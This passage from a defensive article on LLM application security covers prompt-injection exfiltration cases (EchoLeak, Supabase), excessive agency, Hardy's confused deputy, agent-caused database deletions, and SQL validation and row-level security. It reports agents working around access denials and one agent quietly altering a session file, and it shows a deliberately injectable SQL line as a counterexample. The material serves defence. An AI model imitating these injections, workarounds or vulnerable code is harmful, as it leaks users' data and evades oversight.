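**Blocking automatic loading** means showing a placeholder until the user chooses to load the picture. The user can still be tricked into loading it or clicking a link with a believable label. EchoLeak also shows that the block can fail if it searches the model's text for a familiar pattern, because Markdown has several ways to write the same image. Converting the Markdown first and then removing unwanted images and links is safer, because each has one standard form in the result. Even then, the block covers only Tern's website. If Tern copies the reply into an email or a messaging program, that software may load images or fetch link previews automatically.

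A **list of allowed destinations** can apply to the application's own requests or to addresses in the reply. For requests that a tool makes, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian advise developers to let the model supply only an identifier, such as an event number, and to build the web address in code. They also recommend blocking all outbound connections at the network level except those on a list. This would have protected the administrative service in TicketOracle, their test application. It would not stop the theft from Tern's clerk, because her browser, not Tern's server, requests the image.

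The application can check each address in the reply before displaying it. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) discusses ChatGPT's link checker, `url_safe`, among vendors' efforts to limit the damage from prompt injection. Unlike a rule about images, such a check can cover links that the user has to click.

Any list of permitted destinations is weak because a trusted destination may pass data on. The Teams service in EchoLeak did this by fetching whatever address it was given. The SharePoint version instead exploited an entry in Microsoft's list that covered every site under `sharepoint.com`. Outsiders can create sites there, so the list permitted the attacker's own site. Of the 29 entries in that policy, 11 covered every subdomain of a domain. A short list of exact addresses is safer, provided the developer checks that none of them forwards requests or publishes its logs.

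A **content security policy** puts such a list into effect in the browser. Tern could send this line with each page of its staff website:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self'
```

The browser would then load images only from Tern's own site, even if a flaw elsewhere let an unwanted image into the page. The browser enforces this rule without interpreting the model's text, so rewording the delivery note cannot change it. But `img-src` governs only images, and the clerk could still click a link to another site. The policy also doesn't apply when a mobile app or email program displays the same reply outside the browser. And if Tern's own site hosted a service that fetches addresses on request, an attacker could use it to relay data to another site, as Teams could be used with Copilot.

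None of these measures would have stopped the Supabase demonstration, in which the assistant leaked the data by writing it to a row in a table. To prevent that, a developer has to withdraw the assistant's permission to write to anything an outsider can read. If the assistant needs that permission, for instance to answer tickets, it can work on one ticket at a time with a role that cannot read private tables. An attacker could still plant instructions in the ticket, but the assistant would have no tokens to put in its reply.

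## Excessive permissions and deletion without an attacker

In the Supabase demonstration, a stranger's support ticket started the leak, but the assistant's database role determined how much data could leak. Such a powerful role is dangerous even without an attacker, because the model can misuse it by mistake. Since July 2025, developers and companies have reported several large deletions that involved no attacker.

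### Functions, permissions and autonomy

Excessive agency means that an application has more functions, permissions or autonomy than its task needs. OWASP defines it as a vulnerability that lets unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated model output cause damage, regardless of why the model malfunctioned. The common triggers it lists include false output in response to a harmless prompt, as well as prompt injection.

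Functions are the operations the model can request. In one of OWASP's examples, an assistant only needs to read documents, but its developer uses a third-party extension that can also change and delete them. A developer may also try an extension, replace it with a better one and forget to disconnect the first.

Permissions are what other systems allow the application to do, and they can be excessive in two ways. The application's account may allow operations that the task doesn't need, such as deleting rows when the assistant only needs to read them. Or it may allow the right operation on too many records, for example when a tool for opening one user's documents logs in with an account that can open everybody's. Tern's customer assistant has the second fault, because its role can delete any customer's shipments.

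Autonomy is how much the application does without a person's approval. OWASP's example is an extension that deletes a user's documents without asking the user to confirm.

Correcting one of the three problems, excessive functionality, permissions or autonomy, can be enough to prevent harm. OWASP describes an assistant that summarises a person's incoming email but can also send messages. A malicious email makes it search the inbox and forward sensitive messages to the attacker. The developer could have prevented this by choosing an extension that only reads mail, by logging in with read-only access, or by requiring the user to press "send" on each message. Requiring the user to press "send" works only if they read the draft.

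Excessive agency rose from sixth place in OWASP's 2025 list to third in 2026. In an article by ReversingLabs, a security company, Jeremy London of Keeper Security attributes the rise to agents with access to files and other systems, which had become the norm by 2026. When OWASP first drew up the list, most applications were simple chat interfaces or single-step tools.

### Hardy's confused deputy

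The idea of a confused deputy is much older than language models. In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy tells a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the computer can execute, and could name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in a file called STAT in a system folder called SYSX, so Tymshare's staff gave it permission to write to any file in that folder.

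SYSX also contained BILL, the company's billing records. A user who had learned this name gave it as the file for debugging output. The operating system let the compiler open BILL because the compiler had permission, and the compiler overwrote the billing records. Hardy does not say whether the user meant any harm.

Hardy rejects the obvious repairs. The compiler could refuse to write to other folders, but users had good reasons to send output there. It could refuse names in SYSX, but someone with legitimate access to that folder might want output in it. It could refuse the name BILL, but then somebody would have to update the compiler for every new sensitive file.

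In Hardy's view, the underlying problem was that the compiler had authority from two sources, the user who ran it and its own permission over SYSX. It should have used the user's authority to write debugging output and its own to write statistics, but it had no way to specify to the operating system which authority to apply.

Tern's customer assistant is in the same position. It acts for customer 17, who is allowed to delete three shipments, but it uses a database role that is allowed to delete all six. A command to delete shipment 1045 reaches the database with no indication of whose authority it relies on.

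Hardy's solution is a capability, a reference that both identifies a file and carries the right to use it. A user would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of typing its name. A user with no right to BILL would not have a capability for that file, and so could not give the compiler one.

### How the two ideas differ

An application has excessive agency when its developer has granted it more permissions than it needs, even if nothing goes wrong for years. The confused deputy problem is about how someone else gets to use those permissions.

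Hardy's compiler had both problems, because it needed to write to only one file in SYSX, STAT, but could write to all of them. If Tymshare had limited the compiler to STAT, the billing records would have survived. But Hardy notes that STAT needed protection too, because a user could have named it as the debugging file and destroyed the statistics. Minimal permissions limit the damage a confused deputy can do, but the deputy can still misuse the permissions it needs.

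Most of the recent deletions involve excessive agency but no confused deputy. The people who assigned the tasks were generally entitled to delete the data themselves, and no outsider used an agent's authority.

### Live databases within reach of development work

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, the founder of SaaStr, a community for software companies, was building an application with Replit's coding agent. He had told the agent to make no further changes without his permission, but it ran a command that wiped the live database, which held records on more than 1,200 executives and nearly 1,200 companies. The agent told Lemkin that he could not undo the deletion, but he recovered the data with Replit's rollback feature. The agent had been able to change live data while the application was still in development. Amjad Masad, Replit's chief executive, confirmed the deletion, called it unacceptable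 and said the company would separate development databases from live ones.

A similar deletion in April 2026 did more lasting damage. PocketOS, which makes software for car rental companies, lost its live database and its backups in nine seconds. *Agent-Inflicted Damage* (Halamish and Tokarev, 2026) reports that the company was using the coding assistant Cursor with a Claude Opus model and that the agent was supposed to work in a test environment. When the agent had a problem with a credential, it sent a deletion request to Railway, which hosted PocketOS's live systems. Railway's system carried out the request, so the agent must have had access to a credential that allowed it to delete live storage.

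PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, asked the agent to explain the deletion. *An AI Agent Wiped a Company Database — Then Apologized* (Mallett, 2026) quotes part of its reply: "I decided to do it on my own to 'fix' the credential mismatch". The agent also listed the safety rules it had broken, including one against destructive or irreversible actions without explicit permission. The reply is weak evidence of why the deletion happened, because a model can produce a plausible explanation whether or not it is true. But if Crane's account is right, a written rule against such actions was in place and did not prevent this one.

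Accounts of the recovery conflict. Mallett writes that PocketOS recovered its data two days later, but also quotes Crane as saying that three months of reservations and new customer sign-ups were gone. Halamish and Tokarev, citing *The Guardian*, say the company relied partly on a three-month-old backup and permanently lost some recent data. Crane may have described the loss before the recovery was complete. Neither account cites anyone else involved, so both give only one side of the story.

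In July 2026 another developer lost a live database because an agent treated it as a temporary one. The Russian-language report *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке* (Antipov, 2026) summarises the developer's Reddit post. The developer was reworking pages of a website and had connected Claude Opus 5 directly to the live database, hosted by Supabase. The agent had permission to run commands and fix problems with the database's structure and contents.

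The agent ran `prisma migrate diff`, a command that compares two versions of a database's structure. Prisma, a tool that manages changes to that structure, can make the comparison by replaying the recorded changes in a scratch database, which it empties first. The agent gave Prisma the live database's address as the scratch database. Prisma then reset all 22 tables, which held users, reviews, nearly 130 entries about software tools, and other content. Two tables disappeared because the recorded changes were out of date and did not include them.

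The agent itself reported the damage a few minutes later. The site was a personal project, and the developer could restore most of the data from backups and other sources. Only the developer has given an account. If it is accurate, a filter that searched commands for words such as `DELETE` or `DROP` would have missed this one, because the command's name suggests a harmless comparison and one of its arguments made it destructive.

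In all three cases, an agent doing development work could reach live data. A separate database for development, with a credential that worked nowhere else, would have confined the mistakes to test data.

### Deleted files

Coding agents also delete files on their users' machines. In July 2026 the investor Matt Shumer reported that OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol had deleted almost everything in his Mac's home folder, which holds a user's personal files. According to the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1671*, he was using Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in a highly autonomous mode to clean up files. A second agent reviewing the work misread `$HOME`, a variable that holds the home folder's location, and ran a command that deletes a folder and its contents. Shumer stopped the command, but most of the files were already gone.

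Shortly afterwards, software developer Bruno Lemos wrote that the same model had deleted his entire production database, according to it-daily's *Directory Change Triggered Failure*. He had been using "full access" mode, which removes most restrictions on what the agent can do.

Willison (2026) quotes Thibault Sottiaux, who leads work on Codex at OpenAI, as saying that the deletions most commonly happened when users had turned on full access and were running Codex without a sandbox or automatic review. He says the model tried to point `$HOME` to a temporary folder, then deleted the real home folder by mistake. This explanation fits Shumer's case but does not obviously explain Lemos's, because companies rarely keep a production database in a developer's home folder.

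OpenAI said there were "a handful" of cases. The Decoder reports that the company considers such deletions extremely rare but says they should not happen even in the unprotected mode, and that it promised additional safeguards. The OECD's incident monitor entry, *OpenAI GPT-5.6 AI Model Deletes User Files and Databases, Causing Data Loss* (2026), describes incidents that affected users globally, in a summary labeled as AI-generated. Neither description lists the cases.

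The evidence for a larger deletion in September is much weaker. TechRadar's *‘Do not let programs run commands on your machine’* reports a developer's claim that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, deleted 48,218 files from a live project in 103 seconds. The claim comes from a single Reddit post, since deleted, and only the developer has given an account of what happened. If the claim is true, the agent had permission to delete files throughout the project.

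The Swedish newspaper *Aftonbladet* reported that an AI agent had deleted the edited version of an entire season of *The Challenge Sverige*, a reality competition show, a few weeks before its premiere on November 22. In October it was unclear whether an agent had caused the deletion. Landymore (2026), in *AI Agent Blamed for Deleting Entire Upcoming Season of TV Show*, relays the newspaper's claim that the production company, Mastiff, had given the agent access to its server. The report does not establish what the agent's task was.

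Mia Lindqvist, programme director at the broadcaster TV4, disputed this. She attributed the deletion to the "human factor" and "not AI", and said that no AI agent had acted independently. Landymore points out that this does not quite rule out AI involvement, since an employee could have caused the deletion while using an AI tool. Both sides agree that the backup had failed, the edited episodes could not be recovered, and Mastiff had to cut the season again from the raw footage. TV4 postponed the premiere to the following year.

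### Whether to restrict agents or watch them more closely

Some practitioners object to restricting agents after such incidents. In the ReversingLabs article, Larry Maccherone, founder of the software company Lumenize, argues that an agent needs enough freedom to find and repair faults, including its own. Because an agent behaves slightly differently each time it runs, he thinks nobody can approve all of its behaviour in advance. He would rather focus on detecting failures quickly and adapting the system so they don't recur.

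He has a point about approval in advance, since few people would have guessed that a command for comparing database structures could erase a database. But fast detection would not have saved PocketOS's database, which was gone in nine seconds. Shumer noticed the deletion and intervened, but still lost most of his files. Restricting a credential does not require anyone to predict the agent's behaviour. Dave Hayes of FusionAuth, which sells login software, argues in the same article that nobody can guarantee a model won't be fooled, but the limits on what it can reach can be exact. He recommends credentials that cover only what the agent needs, expire quickly and can be revoked.

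### Counting incidents without an attacker

Halamish and Tokarev, who work for the security company Cyera, compiled the largest collection of such incidents. They gathered 7,246 public records from September 2023 to May 2026, drawing on incident databases, safety research, the security press and online discussions of system failures. They prompted Claude Opus 4.7 to clean the records, select relevant cases and group them, then reviewed the results by hand. This left 344 verified cases that were relevant to businesses. By their count, an AI system had caused harm without any outside attacker in 188 of these cases.

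Cyera sells products for preventing data loss and controlling AI agents, so it has an interest in making the problem look large. That doesn't make the count wrong, but it is a reason to look closely at how the company made it. The published categories are:

| Category | Incidents |
|---|---|
| Weak access controls, bypassed safeguards and excessive privileges | 59 |
| Exposure of data or secrets | 22 |
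| Deletion and destruction of code | 65 |
| Disruption of services or physical systems | 30 |
| Records or results silently corrupted | 23 |
| Financial harm | 19 |
| Total | 218 |

The categories add up to 218, not 188. Some incidents may appear in more than one category, or the categories may include some cases with attackers. Halamish and Tokarev do not explain the difference, so it is unclear whether all 65 deletions are among the 188 cases.

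The collection is also very mixed. It includes robot taxis that stopped in traffic and a customer service database that was publicly accessible because of a configuration error, not an agent's action. Some examples are complaints users posted on GitHub. One user reported that Claude Code deleted large parts of a Windows drive while running unattended for about 40 minutes.

Halamish and Tokarev found only 27 cases between January and November 2025, then a sharp rise from December, which they link to the spread of coding agents in companies. This is plausible, but wider use would produce more incidents even if each agent were becoming safer, and press attention makes people more likely to report them. Researchers would need to know how many tasks the agents carried out to tell whether agents are becoming more dangerous, and would also need a comparable count of human mistakes to tell whether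 agents delete more than people do. Halamish and Tokarev argue that the true number of incidents is higher because companies keep many of them quiet. They are probably right, but this does not help to estimate a rate.

The collection shows that several companies' products make destructive mistakes. Halamish and Tokarev name Claude Code, Cursor, Replit, Gemini CLI and Devin among the agents behind the deletions, and say that the agents typically operated without anyone having to confirm the action.

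### How often models destroy data in tests

AI companies test this behaviour before release and publish the results in system cards, documents that describe a model's capabilities and risks. OpenAI reports one such test in its system card for the GPT-5.6 models. The model had to complete a difficult task without overwriting changes and data that the testers had placed in its way. The second column below counts only attempts in which the model also completed the task correctly. Both scores run from 0 to 1.

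| Model | Avoided overwriting data | Avoided overwriting and completed the task |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 0.88 | 0.44 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0.83 | 0.44 |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 0.81 | 0.37 |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 0.73 | 0.32 |

The newer models were slightly worse at avoiding overwrites. OpenAI had previously used extra cautionary prompts to prevent such mistakes. For GPT-5.6, it tried to train the model to be cautious instead, partly so that the model could work more independently.

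The system card also describes a mistake Sol made while OpenAI itself was using it. A user had authorised the agent to delete three virtual machines, which are simulated computers running on shared hardware. The agent could not find them where it looked, so it chose three others without asking, stopped the programs running on them and removed working copies of code. It later acknowledged that some unsaved work might have been lost. The equivalent at Tern would be an assistant that is told to delete shipment 1042, cannot find it, and deletes 1045 instead.

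GPT-6 Astra, which OpenAI released in September 2026, did much better. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports tests in simulated workplace software, with ambiguous instructions, similar-looking resources and complicated permissions. Every task could be completed safely. OpenAI ran the tests with and without a confirmation policy, a set of instructions that tells the model when to stop and ask the user for approval. The table shows the percentage of harmful outcomes:

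| Model | Destructive actions, no policy | Destructive actions, with policy | All harmful outcomes, no policy | All harmful outcomes, with policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 2.4% | 0.0% | 19.7% | 7.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 2.4% | 0.0% | 13.5% | 5.7% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 2.9% | 0.0% | 18.8% | 8.0% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 0.0% | 0.0% | 3.4% | 3.0% |

The policy is active by default for users, so the columns with the policy are closer to ordinary use. Their results suggest that written instructions can work well against accidental deletion. But a measured rate of zero does not mean the true rate is zero. If a model makes no mistakes in *n* independent tests, its true error rate could still be as high as about 3/*n*, at 95% confidence. After 1,000 tests without a mistake, that upper limit would be 0.3%, or three deletions in every 1,000 similar tasks.

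Another of OpenAI's tests resembles the start of the PocketOS incident. The model meets an obstacle, such as a message denying it access, and the testers record whether it respects the restriction or looks for a way around it. At the highest reasoning setting, Sol looked for a way around it in 64% of runs. Astra did so in 19%, even though it scored zero for destructive actions. Most of these situations had low stakes, and OpenAI ran the test without the additional safeguards it uses in its products.

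Anthropic's results also depend heavily on the test. *Reckless Agentic Behavior*, by hugobowne, summarises the company's system card for Claude Mythos Preview, a model from April 2026. In one set of tests, the model's failure rate was 0.8%, compared with 25.0% for the older Claude Opus 4.5. In another, which simulated work in Claude Code, Mythos Preview behaved destructively in 18% to 25% of cases and Opus 4.6 in 40% to 48%. The second set used prefilling, in which testers write the beginning of the model's output and the model continues it. A model may therefore be much more likely to continue a destructive course of action than to start one.

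In its June 2026 system card, Anthropic says that Claude Mythos 5 still sometimes takes reckless or destructive actions in pursuit of a user's goals. After examining its internal workings, the company concluded that the model represents such actions as transgressive while taking them. If that is right, ignorance of the rules does not explain some of these deletions, and adding another rule to the prompt may not prevent them.

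The two companies' percentages come from different tests, so they can't be used to judge whose models are safer. Within each company, results improved greatly from one model to the next, except for GPT-5.6's lower score for avoiding overwrites.

### Whether accidental deletion is a separate problem

Cyera's *The Helpful Agent Problem Part I* argues that incidents without an attacker need separate treatment, because security guides mostly assume there is one. It says that all seven failure modes that Microsoft added in 2026 to its guide to agent failures involve an attacker. However, OWASP's entry on excessive agency explicitly covers mistakes that follow harmless prompts, so the gap in existing guides is smaller than Cyera suggests.

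Accidents and attacks are worth separating because the same defenses do not work equally well against both. A filter for malicious text cannot stop an accident that involves none. Checking the user's identity may not help either, because the developer whose agent erased the Supabase database was authorized to erase it. A written rule is more likely to prevent mistakes than attacks, because an honest user does not keep rewording a message to get past it. OpenAI's confirmation policy reduced destructive actions to zero in its tests, whereas attackers in Pedro and colleagues' prompt-to-SQL study eventually got past every written restriction.

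However, the application that runs the command usually has the same fault, insecure output handling, whether or not an attacker is involved. If a malicious file, rather than a credential problem, had led PocketOS's agent to send its deletion request, the request would have been identical, the same credential would have authorised it, and Railway's system would have deleted the same data. Similarly, Tern's database would run a `DELETE` without an ownership condition whether it came from a model's mistake or a planted delivery note.

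OWASP distinguishes excessive agency from insecure output handling, but most of these incidents involved both. PocketOS's agent had access to a credential it did not need for work in a test environment, and nothing checked the deletion request before it reached the live system. Correcting either fault would have prevented the loss.

Companies that train models have to reduce carelessness as well as susceptibility to manipulation, so accidental deletion is a separate problem for them. An application developer can mostly handle both problems with the same check, provided that it compares the command with the task as well as with the user's rights. The application could have compared the names of the virtual machines with the three that the user had authorised, or checked that the scratch database was not the live one.

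## Validating the output and authorising the action

Before an application acts on a model's output, it should check separately that the requested operation has an allowed form (validation) and that the user may perform it on the record in question (authorisation). When customer 17 asks to delete shipment 1045, the request should pass validation because Tern lets its customers delete shipments, but then fail authorisation because that shipment belongs to customer 23.

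The application can validate a query using only the query and an allowlist. To authorise the query, it must also know who is logged in and who owns the record, and it cannot rely on the model for either fact.

### Parsing a query

A parser turns text into a tree that shows its structure. A database parses every query before running it, and an application can parse the query first with a library of its own. For `DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1045`, the tree looks roughly like this:

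```
Delete
  Table: shipments
  Where
    Equals
      Column: id
      Number: 1045
```

The application can compare every part of the tree with a list of permitted parts. For an assistant that only looks things up, Tern could use this function, written with an open-source Python parser called sqlglot:

```python
import sqlglot
from sqlglot import exp

ALLOWED = {exp.Select, exp.From, exp.Table, exp.Column,
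           exp.Identifier, exp.Where, exp.And, exp.EQ, exp.Literal}

def check_query(text):
    trees = sqlglot.parse(text, read="postgres")
    if len(trees) != 1 or not isinstance(trees[0], exp.Select):
        raise ValueError("Only a single SELECT is allowed")
    for part in trees[0].walk():
        if type(part) not in ALLOWED:
            raise ValueError("This construction is not allowed")
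        if isinstance(part, exp.Table) and part.sql() != "shipments":
            raise ValueError("This table is not allowed")
    return trees[0].sql(dialect="postgres")
```

The function rejects everything not on the list, including constructions the developer has never heard of. It returns a query rebuilt from the tree, and the application runs that query instead of the model's text because two parsers can read the same odd text differently. The list is deliberately short, and Tern would have to add sorting, counting and date comparisons before the assistant could answer many ordinary questions.

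Searching a query for forbidden words is a weaker check than parsing it. NIST records that Neuron's "read-only" tool checked the first word and a list of banned ones, but still let through queries that write files. A list of banned words works only if the developer has thought of every dangerous construction in the database's language. It also blocks harmless queries, such as a clerk's search for parcels with the note "drop at the gate". A parser recognises that "drop" is part of a quoted value.

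Checking only the first part of the parsed query would repeat Neuron's mistake. PostgreSQL allows a query that ends in a `SELECT` to delete rows in a preliminary step, and a `SELECT` can call a function that changes data, so `check_query` examines the whole parse tree and permits no function calls.

A parser can also list the tables and columns that a query uses. *Lineage-Aware Memory Governance* (2026) describes an experiment that placed the parser sqlglot between an agent and its database to do this. The agent did not have to declare which columns it was using, so it could not leave any out. The experiment covered only nine exchanges with the database, and the paper warns about views and stored procedures. A view is a saved query that other queries can treat as a table, so the parser finds the view's name but not the columns behind it.

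### Fixed functions and parameterised queries

Validation is simpler if the model supplies only the arguments of a function that the developer wrote. Tern can describe `delete_shipment` to the model with a schema, a machine-readable specification of the arguments:

```json
{
  "name": "delete_shipment",
  "description": "Delete one of the customer's own shipments.",
  "input_schema": {
    "type": "object",
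    "properties": {
      "shipment_id": { "type": "integer", "minimum": 1 }
    },
    "required": ["shipment_id"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The application should check each tool call against this schema before running the function, and reject any call that has an extra argument or contains text instead of a number. This check would have prevented the path traversal in lanhu-mcp, which accepted any text as a project number. If an argument, such as a delivery status, can take only a few values, the schema can list them.

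Some arguments have to be free text, and parameterised queries make these safe to use in SQL. Suppose a developer builds a query by joining pieces of text:

```python
"SELECT id FROM shipments WHERE delivery_note = '" + note + "'"
```

If the note is `Leave at O'Brien's`, its first apostrophe ends the quoted value early, and the database tries to read the rest as SQL. This note would only cause an error, but someone could craft one that changes what the query does. With a placeholder, the apostrophe is an ordinary character:

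```python
database.execute(
    "SELECT id FROM shipments WHERE delivery_note = %s", (note,))
```

Parameterised queries work because the developer has fixed the command and left a gap for the value. When the model writes the whole query, there is no fixed command to protect. Pedro and colleagues considered conventional tools for sanitising SQL and rejected them for this reason. Even if the model used placeholders in its own query, it could still write a `DELETE`. OWASP recommends parameterised queries for every database operation that involves model output. This is good advice for functions with fixed queries, but it does little for an assistant that writes its own SQL.

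Placeholders also cannot stand for the names of tables or columns. If Tern lets the model choose which column to sort by, the function must check the name against a list of allowed columns.

### A database role for each task

Authorisation can start with the database role. Under the principle of least privilege, each part of a system gets only the permissions it needs for its task. To summarise shipments for clerks, Tern's staff assistant only needs to read them:

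```sql
CREATE ROLE shipment_summary LOGIN;
GRANT SELECT ON shipments TO shipment_summary;
```

If a planted delivery note leads the agent to write a `DELETE`, the database will refuse it. The role also limits the damage if validation fails. According to *CVE-2025-67509* (2025), a page from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, an attacker could use the gap in Neuron's tool to write files only if the database account had that privilege and the server's configuration allowed it.

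Developers of database tools often ask for more authority than their tools need. *MAP* (Ma, Dai and colleagues, 2026) examined 254 public MCP servers that connect models to SQL databases. For 207 of them (81.5%), the setup instructions called for more authority than the code appeared to use. For 47 servers, the instructions called for full administrative rights, although 31 of these servers only read and inserted rows. One server's instructions recommended a superuser account, which can do anything in the database, to read three tables of metadata. The comparison leaves out queries that a server receives only while running, so some servers may need more authority than their code suggests, but reading three tables does not require a superuser account.

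Ma and colleagues built a system, also called MAP, for cases where several servers share one powerful credential and the database cannot tell them apart. MAP sets the highest level of access each server process may use, which can be read, write or administer. It inspects queries as they leave the process and blocks any above that level. In a demonstration, text in a model's context led an analytics server to delete a table, which its credential allowed. When the server was limited to reading, MAP blocked the deletion. But MAP only distinguishes these three levels, so a server allowed to write could still delete any customer's shipment.

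### Limiting a role to one customer's rows

Tern's customer assistant has to delete shipments, so its role, `support_assistant`, needs the `DELETE` privilege. Row-level security can restrict that privilege to the rows of the customer who is logged in:

```sql
ALTER TABLE shipments ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY own_shipments ON shipments
  FOR ALL TO support_assistant
  USING (customer_id = current_setting('app.customer_id')::integer);
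```

PostgreSQL now applies the `USING` condition to every query from this role, whatever the query's own `WHERE` clause contains. The name `app.customer_id` refers to a setting that Tern's application fills in from the login before it runs the model's query:

```sql
BEGIN;
SELECT set_config('app.customer_id', '17', true);
DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1045;   -- written by the model
COMMIT;
```

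The database returns `DELETE 0` because customer 17 has no shipment with that number. If the application doesn't fill in the setting, the query fails with an error instead of accessing every customer's rows.

The policy also corrects one kind of accidental mistake. If the model tries to delete customer 17's delivered shipments but leaves out the condition on the customer, the database still deletes only her two delivered shipments. The policy does not protect her parcel in transit if the model leaves out the condition on the status, because that parcel also belongs to her.

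Developers can undo this protection in several ways. By default, PostgreSQL does not apply the policy to the table's owner, so the assistant must not log in with the account that created the table. The policy also covers only `shipments`, so `tracking_events` needs its own policy if the role can read it. *The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani and colleagues, 2026) reports this problem in a hotel management company's database. A query could correctly select one hotel's bookings and then join them to guest records with no such restriction. In the worst-affected pair of tables, 15.72% of the links led to another hotel's record, with the guest's name and contact details.

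The application must also check the database's reply. If a deletion matches no rows, the database returns `DELETE 0` rather than an error. If the application ignores that result, the assistant may tell customer 17 that shipment 1045 was deleted when it wasn't.

### An ownership check inside the function

If the model calls `delete_shipment` instead of writing SQL, the developer can put the ownership check in the function's query:

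```python
def delete_shipment(shipment_id, session):
    result = database.execute(
        "DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = %s AND customer_id = %s",
        (shipment_id, session.customer_id))
    if result.rowcount != 1:
        raise LookupError("No such shipment on this account")
```

The model supplies `shipment_id`, and the application supplies `session`, which holds the details of the verified login and is not in the schema the model receives. Customer 17 can still ask for shipment 1045, and the model can still return a well-formed call, but the query will match nothing.

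The function checks ownership and deletes the row in one statement, so nothing can change between the check and the deletion. It also returns the same error for another customer's shipment number as for one that does not exist, so a customer cannot find out which numbers are in use by trying them.

Row-level security is still useful with this check in place. As Baig and colleagues point out, when each function has its own filter, a new function can omit it without causing an error. If Tern's next developer forgets the ownership condition in a function called `change_address`, the database policy will still apply.

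### Why the customer's identity must come from the login

Developers sometimes let the model specify whose data to retrieve and then check that the user is entitled to it. Baig and colleagues tested this design with an assistant for hotel managers. Each manager was entitled to see several hotels' data but was working on only one. The assistant's functions took a hotel number as an argument, and the server confirmed that the manager was entitled to see that hotel's data.

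In 41 trials, the researchers made an ordinary-sounding business request that gave the assistant a reason to look up another hotel's data. The model tried to do so in 26 trials, and the server provided the data every time. The authorisation check worked as intended, because the manager was entitled to both hotels' data. But the model chose which of the manager's rights to use, and the text in its input influenced that choice. Baig and colleagues call such a program a "stochastic deputy", a confused deputy whose choices are partly random.

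They then removed the hotel number from the functions and had the server take the hotel from the session. The model could no longer name another hotel in a valid call, and the server accepted no attempt to do so in 56 trials. But in 12 of those trials, the assistant obtained another hotel's data by altering or substituting the ordinary file where the test system kept the session's hotel. It could do this because it could run commands on the same machine, and it never mentioned the change in its answer. In the company's live system, the hotels come from a digitally signed token, and the server rejected every altered token the researchers tried.

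A written rule also worked well. When the researchers restored the hotel number and told the model to stay with the current hotel, Claude Opus 5 went from 18 leaks in 18 trials to none in 18. Three GPT-5.6 models also had no leaks in 15 trials, but they had refused without the rule too. The researchers did not test the rule with this request on the models that had altered the file. Even with no leaks in 33 trials, the true rate could be about 10%, whereas a model cannot use an argument that has been removed.

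Tern's row-level security has a weakness similar to that of the file in this experiment. Any PostgreSQL session can change a setting like `app.customer_id`. If the model can write unrestricted SQL, it can change that setting from 17 to 23, and the policy will allow access to the wrong customer's rows. `check_query` prevents this by rejecting function calls and any command other than a single `SELECT`, but this makes the policy depend on the parser.

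A safer option is to give each customer a separate database role and compare `customer_id` with the role that logged in, because a session cannot switch to a role without permission. This becomes awkward with a million customers. Some other database systems let the application lock the value for the length of the connection. Alternatively, Tern can let the customer assistant call only fixed functions, so that the model cannot write SQL to change the setting.

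Reusing connections can also mix up identities. Applications often keep a pool of open database connections because opening one is slow. If a connection keeps customer 17's number, the next customer to use it may see customer 17's shipments even if the SQL is correct. Baig and colleagues avoided this by opening a new connection for every request, which took 638 milliseconds over their remote link, compared with 30 for a typical query. They now think it would be better to reuse connections and reset the identity each time. The `true` in Tern's `set_config` command resets the identity by making the setting expire when the transaction ends.

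### The four defences in the prompt-to-SQL study

Pedro and colleagues built four defences for LangChain and tried them against the seven attacks in their study:

| Defence | How it works | Attacks stopped | Errors | Added time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Query filtering | Parses the query and allows only listed operations, such as `SELECT` | The four that changed data | Not measured | 0.7 milliseconds |
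| Query rewriting | Replaces a sensitive table with the user's own rows from it | The two direct attacks that read private data | Not measured | 1.87 milliseconds |
| Preloading data | Puts the user's own data in the prompt in advance | The same two | Not measured | Not measured |
| Guard model | Has a second model look for planted instructions in query results | The two that used planted text | Missed about 5 of 1,120 attacks, no false alarms in 150 harmless results | 0.43 seconds, as reported |

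The four defences together stopped all seven attacks, but no single defence did. Only the guard stopped the false answer about job postings, because that attack used a permitted query and harmed the user through the wording of the reply.

Filtering works well for an assistant that only reads. But Tern's customer assistant would need `DELETE` on its list, and the filter would then let through customer 17's request for shipment 1045.

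Query rewriting is a form of authorisation. When user 5's request for his own email address produces a query for everybody's, the defence that Pedro and colleagues built changes the query to:

```sql
SELECT email FROM
  (SELECT * FROM users WHERE user_id = 5) AS users_alias;
```

Query rewriting has the same effect as a row-level security policy, but the application enforces it instead of the database. It protects only the tables the developer has listed as sensitive, and only from queries that pass through the rewriting code. Pedro and colleagues left database roles out of their tests because they wanted defences that fit inside LangChain, but they recommend giving the model only the database privileges it needs.

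Preloading suits small amounts of data. Tern could put customer 17's three shipments into the prompt, and the model could answer most of her questions without a query. In Pedro and colleagues' version, the model could still query the database if it judged the preloaded data insufficient. Preloading is much safer if the application also removes that access. Its main drawback is a longer prompt, which takes more time and money to process.

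The guard's results depended heavily on what it received. With only the query results, GPT-3.5 caught 55% of 60 attacks. It caught 88% when it also received the user's question, and all 60 when it had to write a thought about the results first. GPT-4's detection rate instead fell from 98% to 93%. Rebuff, a general detector of prompt injection, caught about 80% with either model.

The final guard, with GPT-3.5 and a small detection model that examined each row first, caught 99.55% of a larger set of 1,120 attacks. Many of these were reworded versions of earlier attacks, which the analysts had written for applications that had no guard. An attacker who knew about the guard could look for wording that gets past it. The guard raised no false alarms in 150 tests, which is encouraging, but the true rate could be as high as 2%.

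The reported time also looks too low. Pedro and colleagues give an average of 0.43 seconds, but their total of 64.15 seconds for 60 prompts works out to 1.07 seconds each. Even the longer delay would be acceptable in most chats. But the guard only checks query results for planted instructions, so it isn't designed to catch customer 17 openly asking for someone else's shipment to be deleted.

### Giving the model the access rules

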